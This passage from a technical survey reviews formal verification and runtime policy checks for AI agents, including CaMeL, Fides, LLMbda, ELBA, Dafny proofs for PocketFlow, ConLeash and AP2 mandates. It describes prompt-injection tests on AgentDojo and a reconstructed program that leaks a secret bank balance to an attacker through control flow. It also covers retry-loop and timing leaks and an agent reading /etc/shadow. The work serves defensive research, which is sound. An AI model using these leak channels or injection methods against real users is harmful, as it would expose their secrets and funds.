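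CaMeL makes these checks at run time, on plans written in a restricted form of Python. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) points out that this language still has reflection, exceptions and types known only at run time, which make plans hard to check in advance. Nikolaou and colleagues nevertheless check each plan before any tool runs, by converting it into a finite set of states and giving that to a model checker. The model checker can prove that the plan never sends money to a recipient taken from an untrusted source. It can also prove liveness properties, such as "the plan eventually closes every incident ticket it opens", which a monitor that only halts programs cannot enforce. The method assumes that a loop may repeat any number of times, so it rejects some safe plans.

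Fides is more flexible than a system that fixes its plan in advance. It replaces data with a variable name only if reading the data would make the planning model's context less trusted or more secret. The planning model can also send the quarantined model a yes-or-no question, such as whether any email contains a meeting request. An attacker who controls the answer can pass only one bit to the planner, which is hardly enough for an instruction, so a policy may let the planner act on the answer. With its rules on, Fides completed 48% of the Slack tasks, compared with 20% for the basic agent.

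### Noninterference for agents

Labels easily stop an agent from copying a secret bank balance into an email. It is harder to stop the balance from influencing whether the agent sends an email at all. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, found that CaMeL can miss this. The following program, a reconstruction of their example, uses a trick that they trace back to a paper by Fenton from 1974:

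```
rich = True
tmp = True
if balance > 1000:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email(attacker, "rich")
```

CaMeL marks a variable as secret when a branch that depends on a secret changes it, but only if the program takes that branch. Suppose a program reads a secret balance, and its variables tmp and rich both start as True and public. If the balance is 5,000, the program sets tmp to False, and CaMeL marks tmp as secret. The program then skips "rich = False", so rich stays True and public, and CaMeL allows the email. If the balance is 500, tmp stays True and public, so the program sets rich to False and sends no email. The attacker learns which case holds, although no single step breaks a rule.

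The ordinary Python loop around CaMeL's interpreter can also leak information, because it retries failed plans. Whether the policy blocks a plan can depend on a secret, so each attempt can reveal one bit of it. Twenty attempts would be enough to determine an account balance exactly if it is a whole number from 0 to 1,048,575.

Noninterference rules out the email trick because what the attacker sees depends on the balance. Costa and colleagues chose not to require it of Fides because, in their view, it would amount to banning any tool with publicly visible effects once the agent has read a secret. They show that Fides can instead enforce explicit secrecy, which prevents the agent from copying secrets directly but doesn't prevent an outsider from inferring information about them from the agent's choice of actions.

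Garby and colleagues prove noninterference for LLMbda, a small programming language for writing agents. A program can send prompts to a language model, run code that the model returns, and start separate conversations. Every value and every conversation has a label. The run stops if a branch that depends on a secret would add a message to a public conversation.

#### The theorem with probabilities

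Language models answer at random, so the theorem has to compare probabilities. Let μ(q) be the probability that a run finishes with the public outcome q when the secret has one value, and ν(q) the same for another value. Either may add up to less than 1, because some runs never finish or stop at a policy violation. Garby and colleagues call μ and ν compatible if some third distribution, with a total of at most 1, is at least as large as both for every outcome. This amounts to

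Σ_q max(μ(q), ν(q)) ≤ 1.

Suppose an agent tells a supplier that payment will come either on Tuesday or on Friday, and the bank balance is secret. With a low balance, each answer has a probability of 0.5. If a high balance gives probabilities of 0.6 and 0.4, adding the larger probability of each answer gives 0.6 + 0.5 = 1.1, so the program violates the condition. If a high balance instead gives 0.5 for Tuesday, 0.3 for Friday and 0.2 for not finishing, the sum is 0.5 + 0.5 = 1, which is allowed. The secret may therefore affect whether a run finishes, but nothing else about the result. The theorem states that every LLMbda program satisfies this condition, whatever the language model writes.

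Some tasks require an agent to act on untrusted data, such as when a user wants it to read a bill and pay it. For these exceptions, LLMbda has an "endorse" command that marks untrusted data as trusted. A second theorem shows that endorsing data never weakens the protection of secrets.

Garby and colleagues checked these proofs in Lean, and the interpreter that runs the agents is the same Lean program that the theorems describe. The proofs do not cover the code that contacts the language model over the network. The theory also assumes that all tools and data sources are part of the LLMbda program, which is true of a simulated bank but not of a real one.

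### Which guarantees have proofs?

The systems differ in when they check a program and in how firmly anyone has established that the checks work.

| System | Before the program runs | While it runs | Proof |
|---|---|---|---|
| ELBA | Types | Information-flow labels, file paths | On paper, assuming the guarantees of the host language |
| TACIT | Types with capture sets | File paths, website names, permitted commands | Mechanised for the basic type system, still missing for safe mode |
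| CaMeL | Nothing, unless one adds CaMeLoT | Labels and policies | None |
| Fides | Nothing | Labels and policies | On paper, for explicit secrecy |
| LLMbda | Nothing | Labels and policies | Mechanised, for noninterference |

The system with the strongest theorem has no static types, and ELBA tracks information-flow labels at run time rather than in the type checker. ELBA uses LIO, an existing Haskell library with its own soundness proofs. LIO keeps a label for the whole computation, updates it whenever the program reads something, and raises an error if the program attempts a forbidden write. So a program can pass the type checker and still stop halfway through a task. *Agent libOS* (Zhang, 2026) enforces both capabilities and labels at run time.

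### Results on AgentDojo

AgentDojo is a widely used benchmark for prompt injection, with simulated office, travel, banking and Slack accounts. Zhou and colleagues tested ELBA on its 105 Slack cases, which pair each of 21 user requests with each of 5 attacks. All four models resisted every one of the benchmark's own attacks even with the policies off, so those attacks were no use for testing the policies.

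The researchers therefore simulated successful attacks. In ELBA, a subagent reads each piece of outside data, and its prompt normally contains both its task and the data. They changed ELBA so that if the data contained "TODO:", which marks an injected instruction in the benchmark, the subagent received only the data. It then had no instructions except the attacker's. The researchers ran the 105 cases seven times, for 735 trials for each model and setting.

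| Model | Resisted, policies on | Resisted, policies off | Tasks completed, policies on | Tasks completed, policies off |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 735 | 425 | 351 | 523 |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 735 | 460 | 312 | 557 |
| GPT 5.4 | 735 | 621 | 338 | 558 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 735 | 540 | 294 | 494 |

The perfect scores include 29 runs that AgentDojo had counted as successful attacks. Zhou and colleagues reviewed these by hand and found that the agent had only opened a web address, which the policy permits. Since there were just five attacks, the scores are mainly evidence that the policies cover those five goals and that the code enforces them. It is clearer that the policies made the agent less useful, since they reduced the share of completed tasks from 67–76% to 40–48%.

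With policies on and no attack, CaMeL completed 4 to 6 of the 21 tasks, depending on the model, and ELBA completed 8 to 10. CaMeL has to plan everything before it reads any data, while ELBA's agents can read some data and then write the next program. ELBA took about three times as long as CaMeL.

Garby and colleagues tested an LLMbda agent called Randori on the banking tasks. Randori first tries its program on a simulated account, where tool responses can be trusted, and then runs the finished version on the real one. This avoids the leak through CaMeL's retry loop. Only 2 of 1,296 attacks succeeded. But about two thirds of the attacks needed a tool that a plan for the user's task would never call, so they would usually have failed even without labels.

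With GPT-5.2 and no attack, Randori completed 36 of 48 runs, while CaMeL completed 18 with its policies and 32 without them. The comparison favours Randori because it enforces only some of CaMeL's policies and lets the planning model endorse untrusted data. When the researchers removed the endorse command, Randori's completed runs fell from 36 to 30 with one model and from 31 to 26 with another.

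TACIT's results on AgentDojo are similar. Odersky and colleagues ran all four sets of tasks with two models, and by the benchmark's count 1 of 1,926 attacks succeeded. The agents completed 40% to 64% of the tasks with Gemini 2.5 Pro and 48% to 69% with o4-mini.

### What a permitted program can still do

Some of the lost tasks are impossible under any strict policy. If a user asks an agent to pay a friend whose bank details are on the friend's website, untrusted data has to determine where the money goes. The system can refuse, endorse the data or ask the user. Zhou and colleagues cite *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* for the argument that strict checks are still useful, because a person then needs to approve only the actions that fail them.

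TACIT's guarantees also depend on trusted software, including the Scala compiler, the runtime, about 1,000 lines of library code and the model that reads the secrets. Programmers can mark a library as safe without proving that it is. TACIT also doesn't control what an external command does once an agent has permission to run it, so an agent allowed to run a Python interpreter could do almost anything.

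Secrets can also leak through timing. A pure function can't send a secret anywhere, but it can take a second longer if the first letter of a password is in the first half of the alphabet. Odersky and colleagues exclude such side channels from their guarantee. LLMbda's theorem doesn't cover timing either, and it explicitly allows a secret to affect whether a program finishes.

The hardest cases are actions that the policy permits but the user would not want. In both successful attacks on Randori, the user asked the agent to read a file and make the payment it described, but the attacker had replaced the file with a different payment request. The planning model had endorsed the file's contents, as the task required, so the agent followed the user's instruction and made the attacker's payment. Removing the endorse command would block the attack, but it would also prevent the agent from completing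 the task.

An attacker can do harm without redirecting money or revealing secrets. In the project email example, one message might tell the quarantined model to leave out every delay and report that the work is on schedule. Fides's rules for such messages would let the summary through, because the user asked for one and the manager who receives it is allowed to read everything in it. Costa and colleagues note that a stricter policy could require the text itself to be trusted. But a label records where text came from, not whether it is true, so that policy would also block every accurate summary of the same emails.

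## Can the software around an agent be proved safe whatever the model outputs?

The type systems above check programs that a language model writes. Another approach is to verify the ordinary software that carries out the model's requests, without restricting the model itself. Every agent has such software, usually called an agent framework, which sends the prompt to the model, reads the reply and performs the action it specifies. The model only produces text, so it needs the framework to open a file or call a tool. If the framework provably blocks every forbidden action, the agent can't perform one through it, whatever the model outputs.

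Moon and Varshney carried out such a proof for PocketFlow, a very small agent framework, using the verification language Dafny.

### A model that may output anything

In the Dafny program, the language model is a procedure with a name and a result type, Action, but no code. The verifier can therefore assume only that the result is some value of type Action, and has to prove the rest of the program correct for every such value. This is the havoc assumption, named after a command in some verification languages that gives a variable an arbitrary value.

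The proof therefore doesn't depend on the network's weights, training or prompt, and it involves no probabilities. It holds even if the model obeys an attacker or picks actions at random. The proof about the car in a cross-wind required the network to satisfy a condition ψ, which a network verifier then checked. Under havoc there is no such condition to check, so the proof is no harder for a larger model.

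A safety proof that holds for any model output is possible only where the software can always keep the system safe by refusing an action. If it refuses to write a file, the file stays unchanged. But a car keeps moving whatever the software refuses, and arbitrary steering could take it off the road. Allowing any model output, known as havoc, also rules out proving that the agent will complete a task, because the model might request only forbidden actions.

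### An agent with two actions

Take an agent that may read any file but may write only in the folder /reports. Its action type has two variants. Read(p) asks for the contents of the file at path p, and Write(p, t) asks the framework to store the text t at p. This part of the framework handles them:

```
method Step(action: Action) {
  match action
    case Read(p)     => ReadFile(p);
    case Write(p, t) => if InFolder(p) { WriteFile(p, t); }
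}
```

Each step produces a boundary event, which is DidRead(p), DidWrite(p) or, after a refusal, Nothing. Under the policy Π, if the event is DidWrite(p), then p must be in the folder.

One could check a program this short directly. A real framework also has a message history, counters and rules about what to do next, most of which are irrelevant to the policy. Moon and Varshney therefore describe the system twice. An abstract model M contains only what the policy needs, and a concrete model I follows the program in detail. They prove that M obeys the policy and that every step of I matches a step of M, which is called a refinement proof.

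In the example, the state of M is the set W of files the agent has written. A permitted write adds p to W and emits DidWrite(p). A forbidden write emits Nothing and a read emits DidRead(p), and neither changes W. The state of I is an ordered log of everything the program has done. A relation R pairs W with every log in which the written files are exactly those in W. A second relation, Q, pairs events of M with events of I, and here it pairs each event with itself.

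The theorem has four conditions:

- Abstract safety: M obeys its policy Π_M for every sequence of actions. It does, because it emits DidWrite(p) only when p is in the folder.
- Matching start: R pairs the initial states. It does, because W and the log both start empty.
- Matching steps: suppose R pairs m with i, and action a takes I from i to i′ with event e. Then the same action can take M from m to some m′ with some event e′, such that R pairs m′ with i′ and Q pairs e′ with e. The example has three cases (a read, a permitted write and a refused write), and M can follow I in each.
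- Policy transfer: for any two steps matched in this way, Π_M(m, a, e′, m′) ⇒ Π_I(i, a, e, i′). This is immediate here, because the events are the same.

It follows that every step of every run of I satisfies Π_I. Take any run of I, with whatever actions the language model chose. R pairs the initial states. If R pairs the states before a step, the matching-steps condition gives a step of M for the same action, and R pairs the states after it. By induction, M has a run with the same actions. That run obeys the policy because abstract safety holds for every sequence of actions, and policy transfer then implies that every step of I's run satisfies Π_I.

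Suppose the model outputs requests to write /reports/may.txt, overwrite /home/keys, and read /home/keys, in that order. The program emits DidWrite(/reports/may.txt), Nothing, and DidRead(/home/keys). In M, W becomes {/reports/may.txt} after the first request and does not change after the other two.

If a programmer had put WriteFile before the folder test, the second request would emit DidWrite(/home/keys), but M emits Nothing for that action. The steps wouldn't match, so Dafny would reject the proof. If both R and Q were loosened until the steps matched, policy transfer would fail instead, because M's step obeys the policy and the program's step breaks it.

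### What Dafny proved about PocketFlow

An agent in PocketFlow is a graph of tasks, and the action that comes out of one task determines which task runs next. Moon and Varshney verified the loop that moves through the graph, for an interface with four kinds of action. They proved three properties:

- The agent reads only files whose path starts with the path of its workspace folder.
- It calls only tools on a fixed list.
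- The number of steps never exceeds a fixed limit.

The proof is split into six Dafny modules, which contain the types, the two models, the refinement conditions, the proof of those conditions and the final theorem. Like the payment agent's proof, it needs helper invariants, for example that the length of the history agrees with the step counter.

Language models wrote most of this. Claude Sonnet 4.6 explored the source code, and Claude Opus 4.7 wrote the specifications and proofs and repaired the ones Dafny rejected. The researchers ran this pipeline four times on two example agents, one that reads files and one that looks up documents to answer questions. Each run used between 1.6 and 3.4 million tokens. Dafny accepted every final proof, taking 1.2 to 2.5 seconds for each path through the graph, but the pipeline's tests missed one property that was only vacuously true. Dafny then translated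 the verified program into Python. The researchers sent the Python version both permitted and forbidden actions, and it recorded only permitted events.

PocketFlow is about the easiest target one could choose. Moon and Varshney note that production frameworks such as LangChain, with dozens of kinds of action, are the real test of whether the method scales.

The final theorem, as printed, is also narrower than "the agent reads only its own files". It states that every path in the program's record of reads begins with the workspace path. To conclude that the agent reads only its own files on disk, one must also know that the record is complete and that the operating system treats every such path as a file in the workspace folder.

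### Effects outside the interface

The missing assumption, which Moon and Varshney call effect exclusivity, is that every effect the agent can have on the outside world passes through the typed interface and appears in the model as a boundary event. The proof does not establish this. Whoever deploys the agent has to arrange it, usually with a sandbox, which uses the operating system to restrict what a process can reach. Sandboxes are generally not formally verified, so Moon and Varshney recommend using one together with the proof and reviewing the code at the interface by hand.

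The full trusted base consists of:

- the policy as written
- effect exclusivity
- the parser that turns the model's text into an Action, and the short piece of code that passes the Action to the verified program
- the Dafny verifier and its compiler to Python
- the Python runtime, the operating system and the hardware, including anything that depends on timing or on several processes running at once.

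Moon and Varshney also list the relations R and Q, which need less trust than the other items because the theorem's conclusion is only about the concrete model and its policy. A badly chosen R or Q makes the proof fail but can't make a false conclusion pass.

None of these items is a property of the language model, so Moon and Varshney argue that the guarantee does not weaken as models become more capable. This is true of the theorem, but its assumptions concern large pieces of ordinary software, and a more capable model is more likely to find a fault in that software.

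The guarantee also depends on how narrow the interface is. If one of the actions is "run this shell command", that action covers nearly everything a computer can do, so little can be proved. Coding agents usually need a shell. *Tether* (Sistla, Solko-Breslin and colleagues, 2026) therefore checks a command's effects instead of its text. It runs each command in a disposable copy of the file system and traces the command's requests to the operating system. It translates these requests into 11 abstract actions, such as read, copy and upload, and applies a policy written in Lean. The changes take effect only if the policy allows all of them.

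On two benchmarks for coding agents, Tether blocked every attack whose actions it could trace, and wrongly blocked 2.3% and 5.0% of harmless runs. But it needs a larger trusted base, which includes the tracing software, the file-system layer, a network proxy and the translation into abstract actions. That translation has to be a cautious guess, so if a script reads one file and then writes another, Tether treats data as having passed between them.

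### Plans, workflows and contracts

In *Guardians of the Agents*, Meijer proposes checking the model's whole plan before any of it runs, much as CaMeLoT does. Existing program-analysis tools can search the plan for data flows that a policy forbids, such as from the user's mailbox into a message to an outside address. For other requirements, Meijer suggests stating what must be true after the plan has run. In one example, the user asks an agent to delete foo.txt and bar.txt, and the model plans to delete every text file, which still meets the requirement that the two files be gone. Preventing this requires a frame condition, which states what must stay the same. Meijer adds one to the description of the deletion tool, but the plan's own requirement also needs one ("no other file changes"), or deleting every text file still counts as correct. The article is a design proposal and reports no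 measurements.

*Lean4Agent* (Wang, Huang and colleagues, 2026) verifies workflows, which are written instructions that divide a task into steps for a model. A language model annotates each step with the conditions it needs and the conditions it should bring about, and Lean checks that earlier steps supply what later ones need. The proof assumes that the model performs every step correctly, whereas havoc allows any output. The check can therefore find gaps in the instructions but gives no protection against a model that ignores them. Across five models, agents using workflows that passed the check solved 58.3% of 50 hard software problems, and agents using workflows that failed it solved 43.5%. On 100 questions about AI papers, the scores were 36.6% and 27.5%. Each benchmark tested only three workflows from each group, so the size of the gap is uncertain.

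Lean4Agent can also check what happened at each step of a run, partly by using another language model, and revise the workflow accordingly. This raised the average score on the software problems from 56.9% to 64.4%. However, the revised workflows were second attempts at the same problems, made after test results were available, so some of the gain may come from the extra attempt.

Ciliberto, Rudi and Tassi (2026), in *Proof-Carrying Contracts*, require an agent to supply a proof with every tool call. In their example, a family's agent hires a travel agency's agent to arrange a three-night trip and obtain a visa. The contract caps spending at 2,000 euros including fees, requires a rating of at least 7 for every hotel, and allows the agency's agent to send the passport only to the consulate. A program called the Airlock holds the passport and the agency's fee of 300 euros, and all tool calls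 go through it. For each call, the agent has to prove, roughly, that for all states s and s′

View(s) = v and C(s) and D(s, s′) ⇒ C(s′),

where v is what the agent can see, C is the contract's conditions, and D(s, s′) means that the call may lead from s to s′. If the agent has already committed 900 euros, it can prove that a booking of up to 1,100 euros stays within the cap. It can't prove this for a larger one. Once the trip is booked and the consulate has granted the visa, the agent can prove that too and collect the fee without asking the family.

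Ciliberto and colleagues prove that the conditions hold from the start of the contract until it closes, for every possible agent, and provide a Lean version of the theory. As with havoc, the theorem requires no assumptions about the model. A framework like PocketFlow must decide whether an action is permitted, while the Airlock only checks the agent's proof, so the contract can contain conditions that no program could decide in general. But the Airlock refuses a safe action if the agent doesn't find a proof in time.

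The theorem also assumes that the agent has no other way to act, that D includes everything a tool might do, that the Airlock's records match the world, and that the conditions provide the protection the parties wanted. Ciliberto and colleagues report no experiments, and their theory so far covers one acting agent under one contract.

### Spending, deletion, network access and judgement

Each policy in Moon and Varshney's theorem is a condition on a single step, based on the state before it, the action, the event and the state after it. Many requirements can be written this way if the state contains the right information.

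| Requirement | Condition on each step | What the state must contain |
|---|---|---|
| Spending cap | The total so far plus this payment and its fees is within the cap | All commitments so far |
| Deletion | Someone has approved the deletion of this particular file | Approvals, file by file |
| Network access | The destination is on a list, and the data sent there is not secret | A secrecy label for each file |
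| Truthfulness | None | Nothing that would settle it |
| Good judgement | None, except through a stand-in such as a rating | The stand-in |

Without this information, a series of permitted steps can add up to harm. A limit of 100 euros per payment allows thirty payments of 100 euros. The two-action agent can read a confidential file and write its contents into /reports. If outsiders can see that folder, the agent has leaked the file, even though both steps were permitted and the proof is correct.

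Sistla and colleagues give the example of an agent that uploads a harmless status report, copies a confidential inventory into the report file, and then uploads the file again. The two upload commands are identical, but only the first is safe. Tether allows the first and blocks the second because copying a file also copies its secrecy label, through any number of intermediate files. Havoc proofs can cover such rules too, if the labels are part of the state.

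*Formal Runtime Verification for Tool-Using LLM Agents* (Kekatos, Lekidis and colleagues, 2026) shows how much depends on this history. It applied five general rules to recorded runs from AgentDojo, including one that requires an approval before any irreversible action. The rules flagged 70.1% of the successful attacks but also 29.3% of the harmless runs. The recordings contain no approvals, so the rules flagged every action of a risky type. In the banking tasks, where the agent's job is to make payments, they flagged 79.2% of the harmless runs.

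A longer history does not help check truthfulness. The state can contain an email's recipient and full text, but whether the text is true depends on facts outside the formal model. For this reason, Moon and Varshney leave truthfulness and deception to other methods.

For matters of judgement, Ciliberto and colleagues let the parties appoint an expert, such as a particular language model with a fixed prompt, whose verdict is treated as true. The Airlock can then establish that a hotel has a recorded rating of 8, but not that the family will like it. It also cannot make up for a condition that nobody wrote down. If a contract requires a flight and a hotel but doesn't require their dates and destinations to match, the family can end up with a flight to one city and a hotel in another, even if every call comes with a correct proof.

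## Which parts of consent can a machine check?

The payment agent's specification requires an approval for every payment. So far, approval has meant only that a payment, such as payment 7, is in the set Approved. Most real consent covers more than one payment and comes with limits. A customer might tell her agent to pay the office suppliers' invoices in March, up to 500 euros each, but never to a new bank account. Someone has to turn this instruction into data before a program can check a payment against it.

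### A formal consent record

Haklidir (2026), in *Consent Chain Degradation in Embodied Multi-Agent Systems*, represents a person's consent to a robot's actions with six fields: the person, the permitted actions, the places, a time window, the exclusions, and a flag for whether the robot may pass the permission on. The flag defaults to "no". For a software agent, the record should also name the agent, the data and the purpose. The customer's instruction then looks like this:

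| Field | Customer's record | What the checker compares it with |
|---|---|---|
| Who consents | The customer | The owner of the account |
| Who may act | Her payment agent | The identity of the program that asks to pay |
| Actions | Payments up to 500 euros | The type and amount of the action |
| Data or place | Office suppliers' invoices, business account | The invoice and the account |
| Purpose | Running the office | The purpose that the agent declares |
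| Time | 1 to 31 March | A trusted clock |
| Exclusions | New bank accounts | A list of accounts she has paid before |
| May the agent pass it on? | No | The chain of agents behind the request |

Purpose is the hardest field to check, because the checker has only the purpose that the agent declares. The other fields depend on data that a well-run system can record reliably.

The core requirement is an invariant:

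∀a ∈ Covered ∃r ∈ Records : Valid(r, time(a)) and a ∈ Scope(r).

An action is covered if it needs consent. A consent record is valid at a given moment if it is genuine, its time window includes that moment and nobody has withdrawn it. An action is within the record's scope if every field of the action matches the record and no exclusion applies. The rule is that no covered action may occur without a valid record whose scope includes it. This is a safety property because once a covered action, such as a payment, occurs without such a record, the property stays violated whatever happens later.

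A single record has to meet all the conditions. Suppose the customer has also allowed the agent to pay her landlord any amount. A payment of 900 euros to a supplier then matches one record on payee and the other on amount, but neither record covers it.

Someone must also decide which actions belong in Covered. If it includes payments but not subscriptions, the invariant holds even when the agent takes out subscriptions without consent. An action that affects several people, such as a withdrawal from a joint account, may need a consent record from each of them.

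Products already in use have broken this invariant. *Temporary Authority, Permanent Effects* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) collects 17 security advisories about flaws, all since fixed, in three agent products. In 12 of them, the product did something the approval didn't cover, such as running a command with arguments that the approval screen had left out. In the other five, the product still relied on an approval after the facts behind it had changed. For example, a user approved a script, and the product ran it after someone had rewritten it.

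### Is the action within scope?

Many agents use tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for connecting language models to other software. The program that runs the agent typically prompts the user to allow a tool once or always. "Always" covers every use of the tool, so a user who chooses it for a search of one project folder also allows a search of her whole computer.

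Li, Khabra and colleagues (2026), in *Options, Not Clicks*, built ConLeash to narrow this down. It describes each tool call by four labels: where the input comes from, where the output goes, how sensitive the data is, and what effects the call has. The labels have an order. For locations on the user's computer it is

exact file ⊑ parent folder ⊑ local computer,

where ⊑ means "lies within". Sensitivity and effects are sets, so {read} lies within {read, write}. A call φ lies within an approved boundary φ′ if all four parts do:

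φ ⊑ φ′ ⇔ input ⊑ input′ and output ⊑ output′ and sensitivity ⊆ sensitivity′ and effects ⊆ effects′.

Mathematicians call this kind of ordering a lattice. It doesn't have to rank every pair of points. For example, a call that reads a secret involves more sensitive data than a call that deletes a public file, but the deletion is more destructive, so neither call ranks above the other.

Suppose the user has allowed the agent to read ordinary files in /project/sales/. The agent then makes two more calls, one for a price list in that folder and one for /etc/shadow, the system file that holds password data.

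| Part | Approved boundary | Read /project/sales/prices.csv | Read /etc/shadow |
|---|---|---|---|
| Input | Parent folder | Exact file: inside | Local computer: outside |
| Output | Agent's context | Agent's context: inside | Agent's context: inside |
| Sensitivity | {ordinary} | {ordinary}: inside | {sensitive}: outside |
| Effects | {read} | {read}: inside | {read}: inside |

ConLeash permits the first call without prompting the user. The second call fails on two parts, and either failure would have been enough to trigger a prompt. The prompt offers her several boundaries of different widths, and ConLeash saves her choice as a new rule. A call to delete the price list would also trigger a prompt, because deletion is not an approved effect.

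A file in /project/secrets/ can have the same four labels as one in /project/src/, so ConLeash also stores a pattern for the permitted path. Users can add bans, such as "never send files outside /project/ to external recipients". As printed, the decision procedure applies the narrowest rule that matches a call, which would let a narrow permission override a broader ban. Li and colleagues state elsewhere that bans always override permissions, so the program has to check bans first.

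#### How well it works

The main test used 3,538 tool calls in 984 sequences. ConLeash permitted 98.3% of the harmless calls without prompting the user and caught 99.4% of the escalations. It caught all 1,440 calls that crossed an approved boundary and missed 15 of the 356 that broke a ban. Because a language model generated the sequences and the researchers worked out the correct decisions by simulating the consent process, the test mainly measures how accurately ConLeash applies its own rules.

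Li and colleagues also replayed 50 real sessions from six software developers. Of the 1,435 calls, 291 crossed a boundary as the researchers defined it. ConLeash caught 278 of these, and "always allow" caught none. Claude Code's automatic mode, in which a language model judges each call, caught six, but its purpose is to stop commands that are dangerous in themselves. In one session, automatic mode let an agent working on one project delete a folder belonging to another project.

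In a small study, 16 people chose a lasting permission in 46.3% of their decisions with ConLeash and 13.3% with the usual buttons. Fifteen preferred ConLeash and one had no preference. Lasting permissions are less risky with ConLeash because each has a boundary.

The comparison of labels is exact and takes about 8 milliseconds. A language model chooses the labels, which takes nearly five seconds, and it can make mistakes. If it labels a password file as ordinary, a correct comparison may still place an unsafe call inside the boundary. The rule language also cannot express time limits such as "allow for today", so ConLeash checks only part of the record above.

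### Signed payment mandates

A checker also has to verify that a record is genuine, especially when the agent delivers it. The Agent Payments Protocol (AP2), which Google announced in 2025, uses digital signatures for this. Only the holder of a private key can produce a valid signature, and anyone with the matching public key can check it. The current specification, *Agentic Payment Protocol (v0.2)*, calls its signed records mandates. A checkout mandate authorises the purchase of particular goods, and a payment mandate authorises payment for them. According to AP2's *Agent Payments Protocol Documentation*, working groups at the FIDO Alliance, an industry body for authentication standards, are taking over further standardisation.

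Suppose a customer wants her agent to buy one pair of shoes, red or blue, and one pair of socks while she is away:

1. The agent drafts two "open" mandates that contain her limits. They may cover the shops, the items, the price range, a total budget and how often the agent may buy.
2. A trusted surface shows her the limits, confirms her identity and signs the mandates. The surface is a screen run by ordinary code with no language model. The mandates include the agent's public key, so another agent can't use them.
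3. The agent fills a basket, and the shop signs the resulting checkout.
4. The agent signs two "closed" mandates for this purchase. Each contains a hash of the checkout.
5. The shop compares the basket with the customer's limits, and the company that holds her card details does the same for the payment.

A basket with red shoes and socks passes, but a basket with red shoes and blue shoes fails, and so does a basket with only socks. If the customer is present, she approves the final checkout directly, so the open mandates aren't needed.

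A valid signature establishes that someone with the private key signed this exact text. The hash also ties the approval to one checkout, so a dishonest agent can't attach it to a more expensive basket. The specification also treats verified mandates as evidence of what the user saw. This depends on the trusted surface working correctly, because a faulty one could show a limit of 100 dollars and sign one of 1,000. AP2 also permits the surface to sign with a key that belongs to the agent's provider, in which case the signature shows only that the provider vouches for the user's approval.

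Signatures also don't prevent reuse, because a copy of a signed mandate is as valid as the original. AP2 forbids the agent from presenting an open mandate again unless the first attempt failed. But the specification treats the agent as a potential attacker, so someone who sees all the payments, such as the card provider, needs to keep count. AP2 also recommends giving open mandates the shortest lifetime that allows the agent to finish. The sample mandate in the documentation lasts an hour.

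### Checking the life cycle

Consent also changes over time, and a model checker can search the possible sequences of changes for mistakes. *Anumati* (Kadaboina, 2026) does this for agents that use other agents' services. Here, consent means that the calling agent accepts a service's terms on behalf of the person it works for. Each consent record uses a hash to identify the exact version of the terms and has an entry for each clause, which the agent can accept or dispute. A separate log records which clause the agent considered before each action and what it decided.

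The model has seven states: idle, terms fetched, under review, accepted, rejected, accepted with some clauses in dispute, and out of date. Kadaboina used the model checker TLC to check seven safety properties (S1 to S7) and two liveness properties (L1 and L2):

| Property | Requirement |
|---|---|
| S1 | No service call occurs unless some record accepts the terms, at least in part |
| S2 | The lists of records and log entries never get shorter |
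| S3 | Every log entry refers to an existing record |
| S4 | Before every call there is a log entry that permits an action under an undisputed clause |
| S5 | A log entry about a disputed clause is always "deny" or "escalate" |
| S6 | No log entry about a disputed clause is "permit" |
| S7 | No call occurs if the calling agent's configuration has changed since it consented |
| L1 | A change in the terms or the configuration eventually leads to a new record |
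| L2 | A change in the configuration eventually leads to renewed consent |

S6 restates S5, and L2 is a special case of L1. More importantly, S1 is weaker than the consent invariant. Suppose an agent accepts version 1 of the terms, rejects version 2 and then calls the service anyway. The old acceptance is still in the list, so S1 holds, and as worded the other eight properties hold too. Kadaboina says the service blocks calls when its terms change, so the model may well exclude this run. But if a mistake in the model allowed it, checking the nine properties would not reveal it.

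#### What the bounds mean

TLC found no violations in any reachable state with up to three policy versions, four log entries per consent and two configuration versions. Within these limits, the search covered every order of events, including ones a human tester would be unlikely to try.

The result doesn't extend to a fourth version or a fifth log entry. If the design overwrote the first log entry when the fifth arrived, this search would miss the error. The liveness results need particular care because the model allows only a few changes of terms, while a service that kept changing its terms might keep an agent re-reading them forever. Kadaboina notes that removing the limits would require a proof by induction, like the one for the payment agent.

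The search also covers only the model. The Python implementation has 35 unit tests but no proof that it follows the model. S7 relies on the calling agent to report its own configuration, which the service can't verify.

None of the seven states represents withdrawal. Consent can go out of date when the terms or the agent change, but the model has no step in which the person changes her mind. Haklidir's framework doesn't model withdrawal yet either.

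### Withdrawing approval for a queued payment

The payment agent's model left withdrawal out for simplicity. Add a fourth transition:

- Withdraw(p) removes payment p from Approved.

Now consider the run

Approve(7), Queue(7), Withdraw(7), Send(7).

It ends with payment 7 sent but not approved, so "Sent ⊆ Approved" is false. The earlier proof fails at the third step because it relied on the helper condition that every queued payment is approved, and withdrawing the approval of a queued payment breaks this condition.

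The remedy is to check again at the last moment, so that Send(p) requires p to be in both Queued and Approved. The specification has to change as well. If the customer withdraws her approval of a payment that went out yesterday, "Sent ⊆ Approved" becomes false although the agent did nothing wrong. The requirement should be about the moment of sending:

every Send(p) step starts in a state where p ∈ Approved.

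The new condition on Send guarantees this directly. Payments whose approval has gone simply stay in the queue.

In the model, steps happen one at a time, but in a real system the customer might withdraw approval after the program checks it and before the program sends the payment. The service that sends the money therefore has to check the approval and make the payment in a single indivisible operation. Santos-Grueiro calls this commit-time authorisation and has proved in Lean that it works, provided that every action goes through this checkpoint and that the policy lists every fact the approval depends on.

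Common agent software doesn't recheck the facts behind an approval before acting on it. In 23 test runs with the LangChain framework, those facts changed after the approval but before the agent acted. The unmodified framework carried out all 28 affected writes, while a protected version blocked them all.

Better models don't solve the problem. In another experiment, the instructions allowed changes only while the approval and the conditions behind it held, and one of these lapsed during the task. Without a notice, GPT-5.6 Sol made an unauthorised change in 25 of 36 runs and Claude Sonnet 5.5 in 30. With a notice, the numbers fell to 1 and 0, but no model can obey a withdrawal that comes after it last checked the approval. Ordinary benchmarks can hide such failures. The benchmark's scorer gave full marks to all 12 runs in which four models carried out a task after losing approval, because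 it checked only the final database.

#### When approvals and payments are in different places

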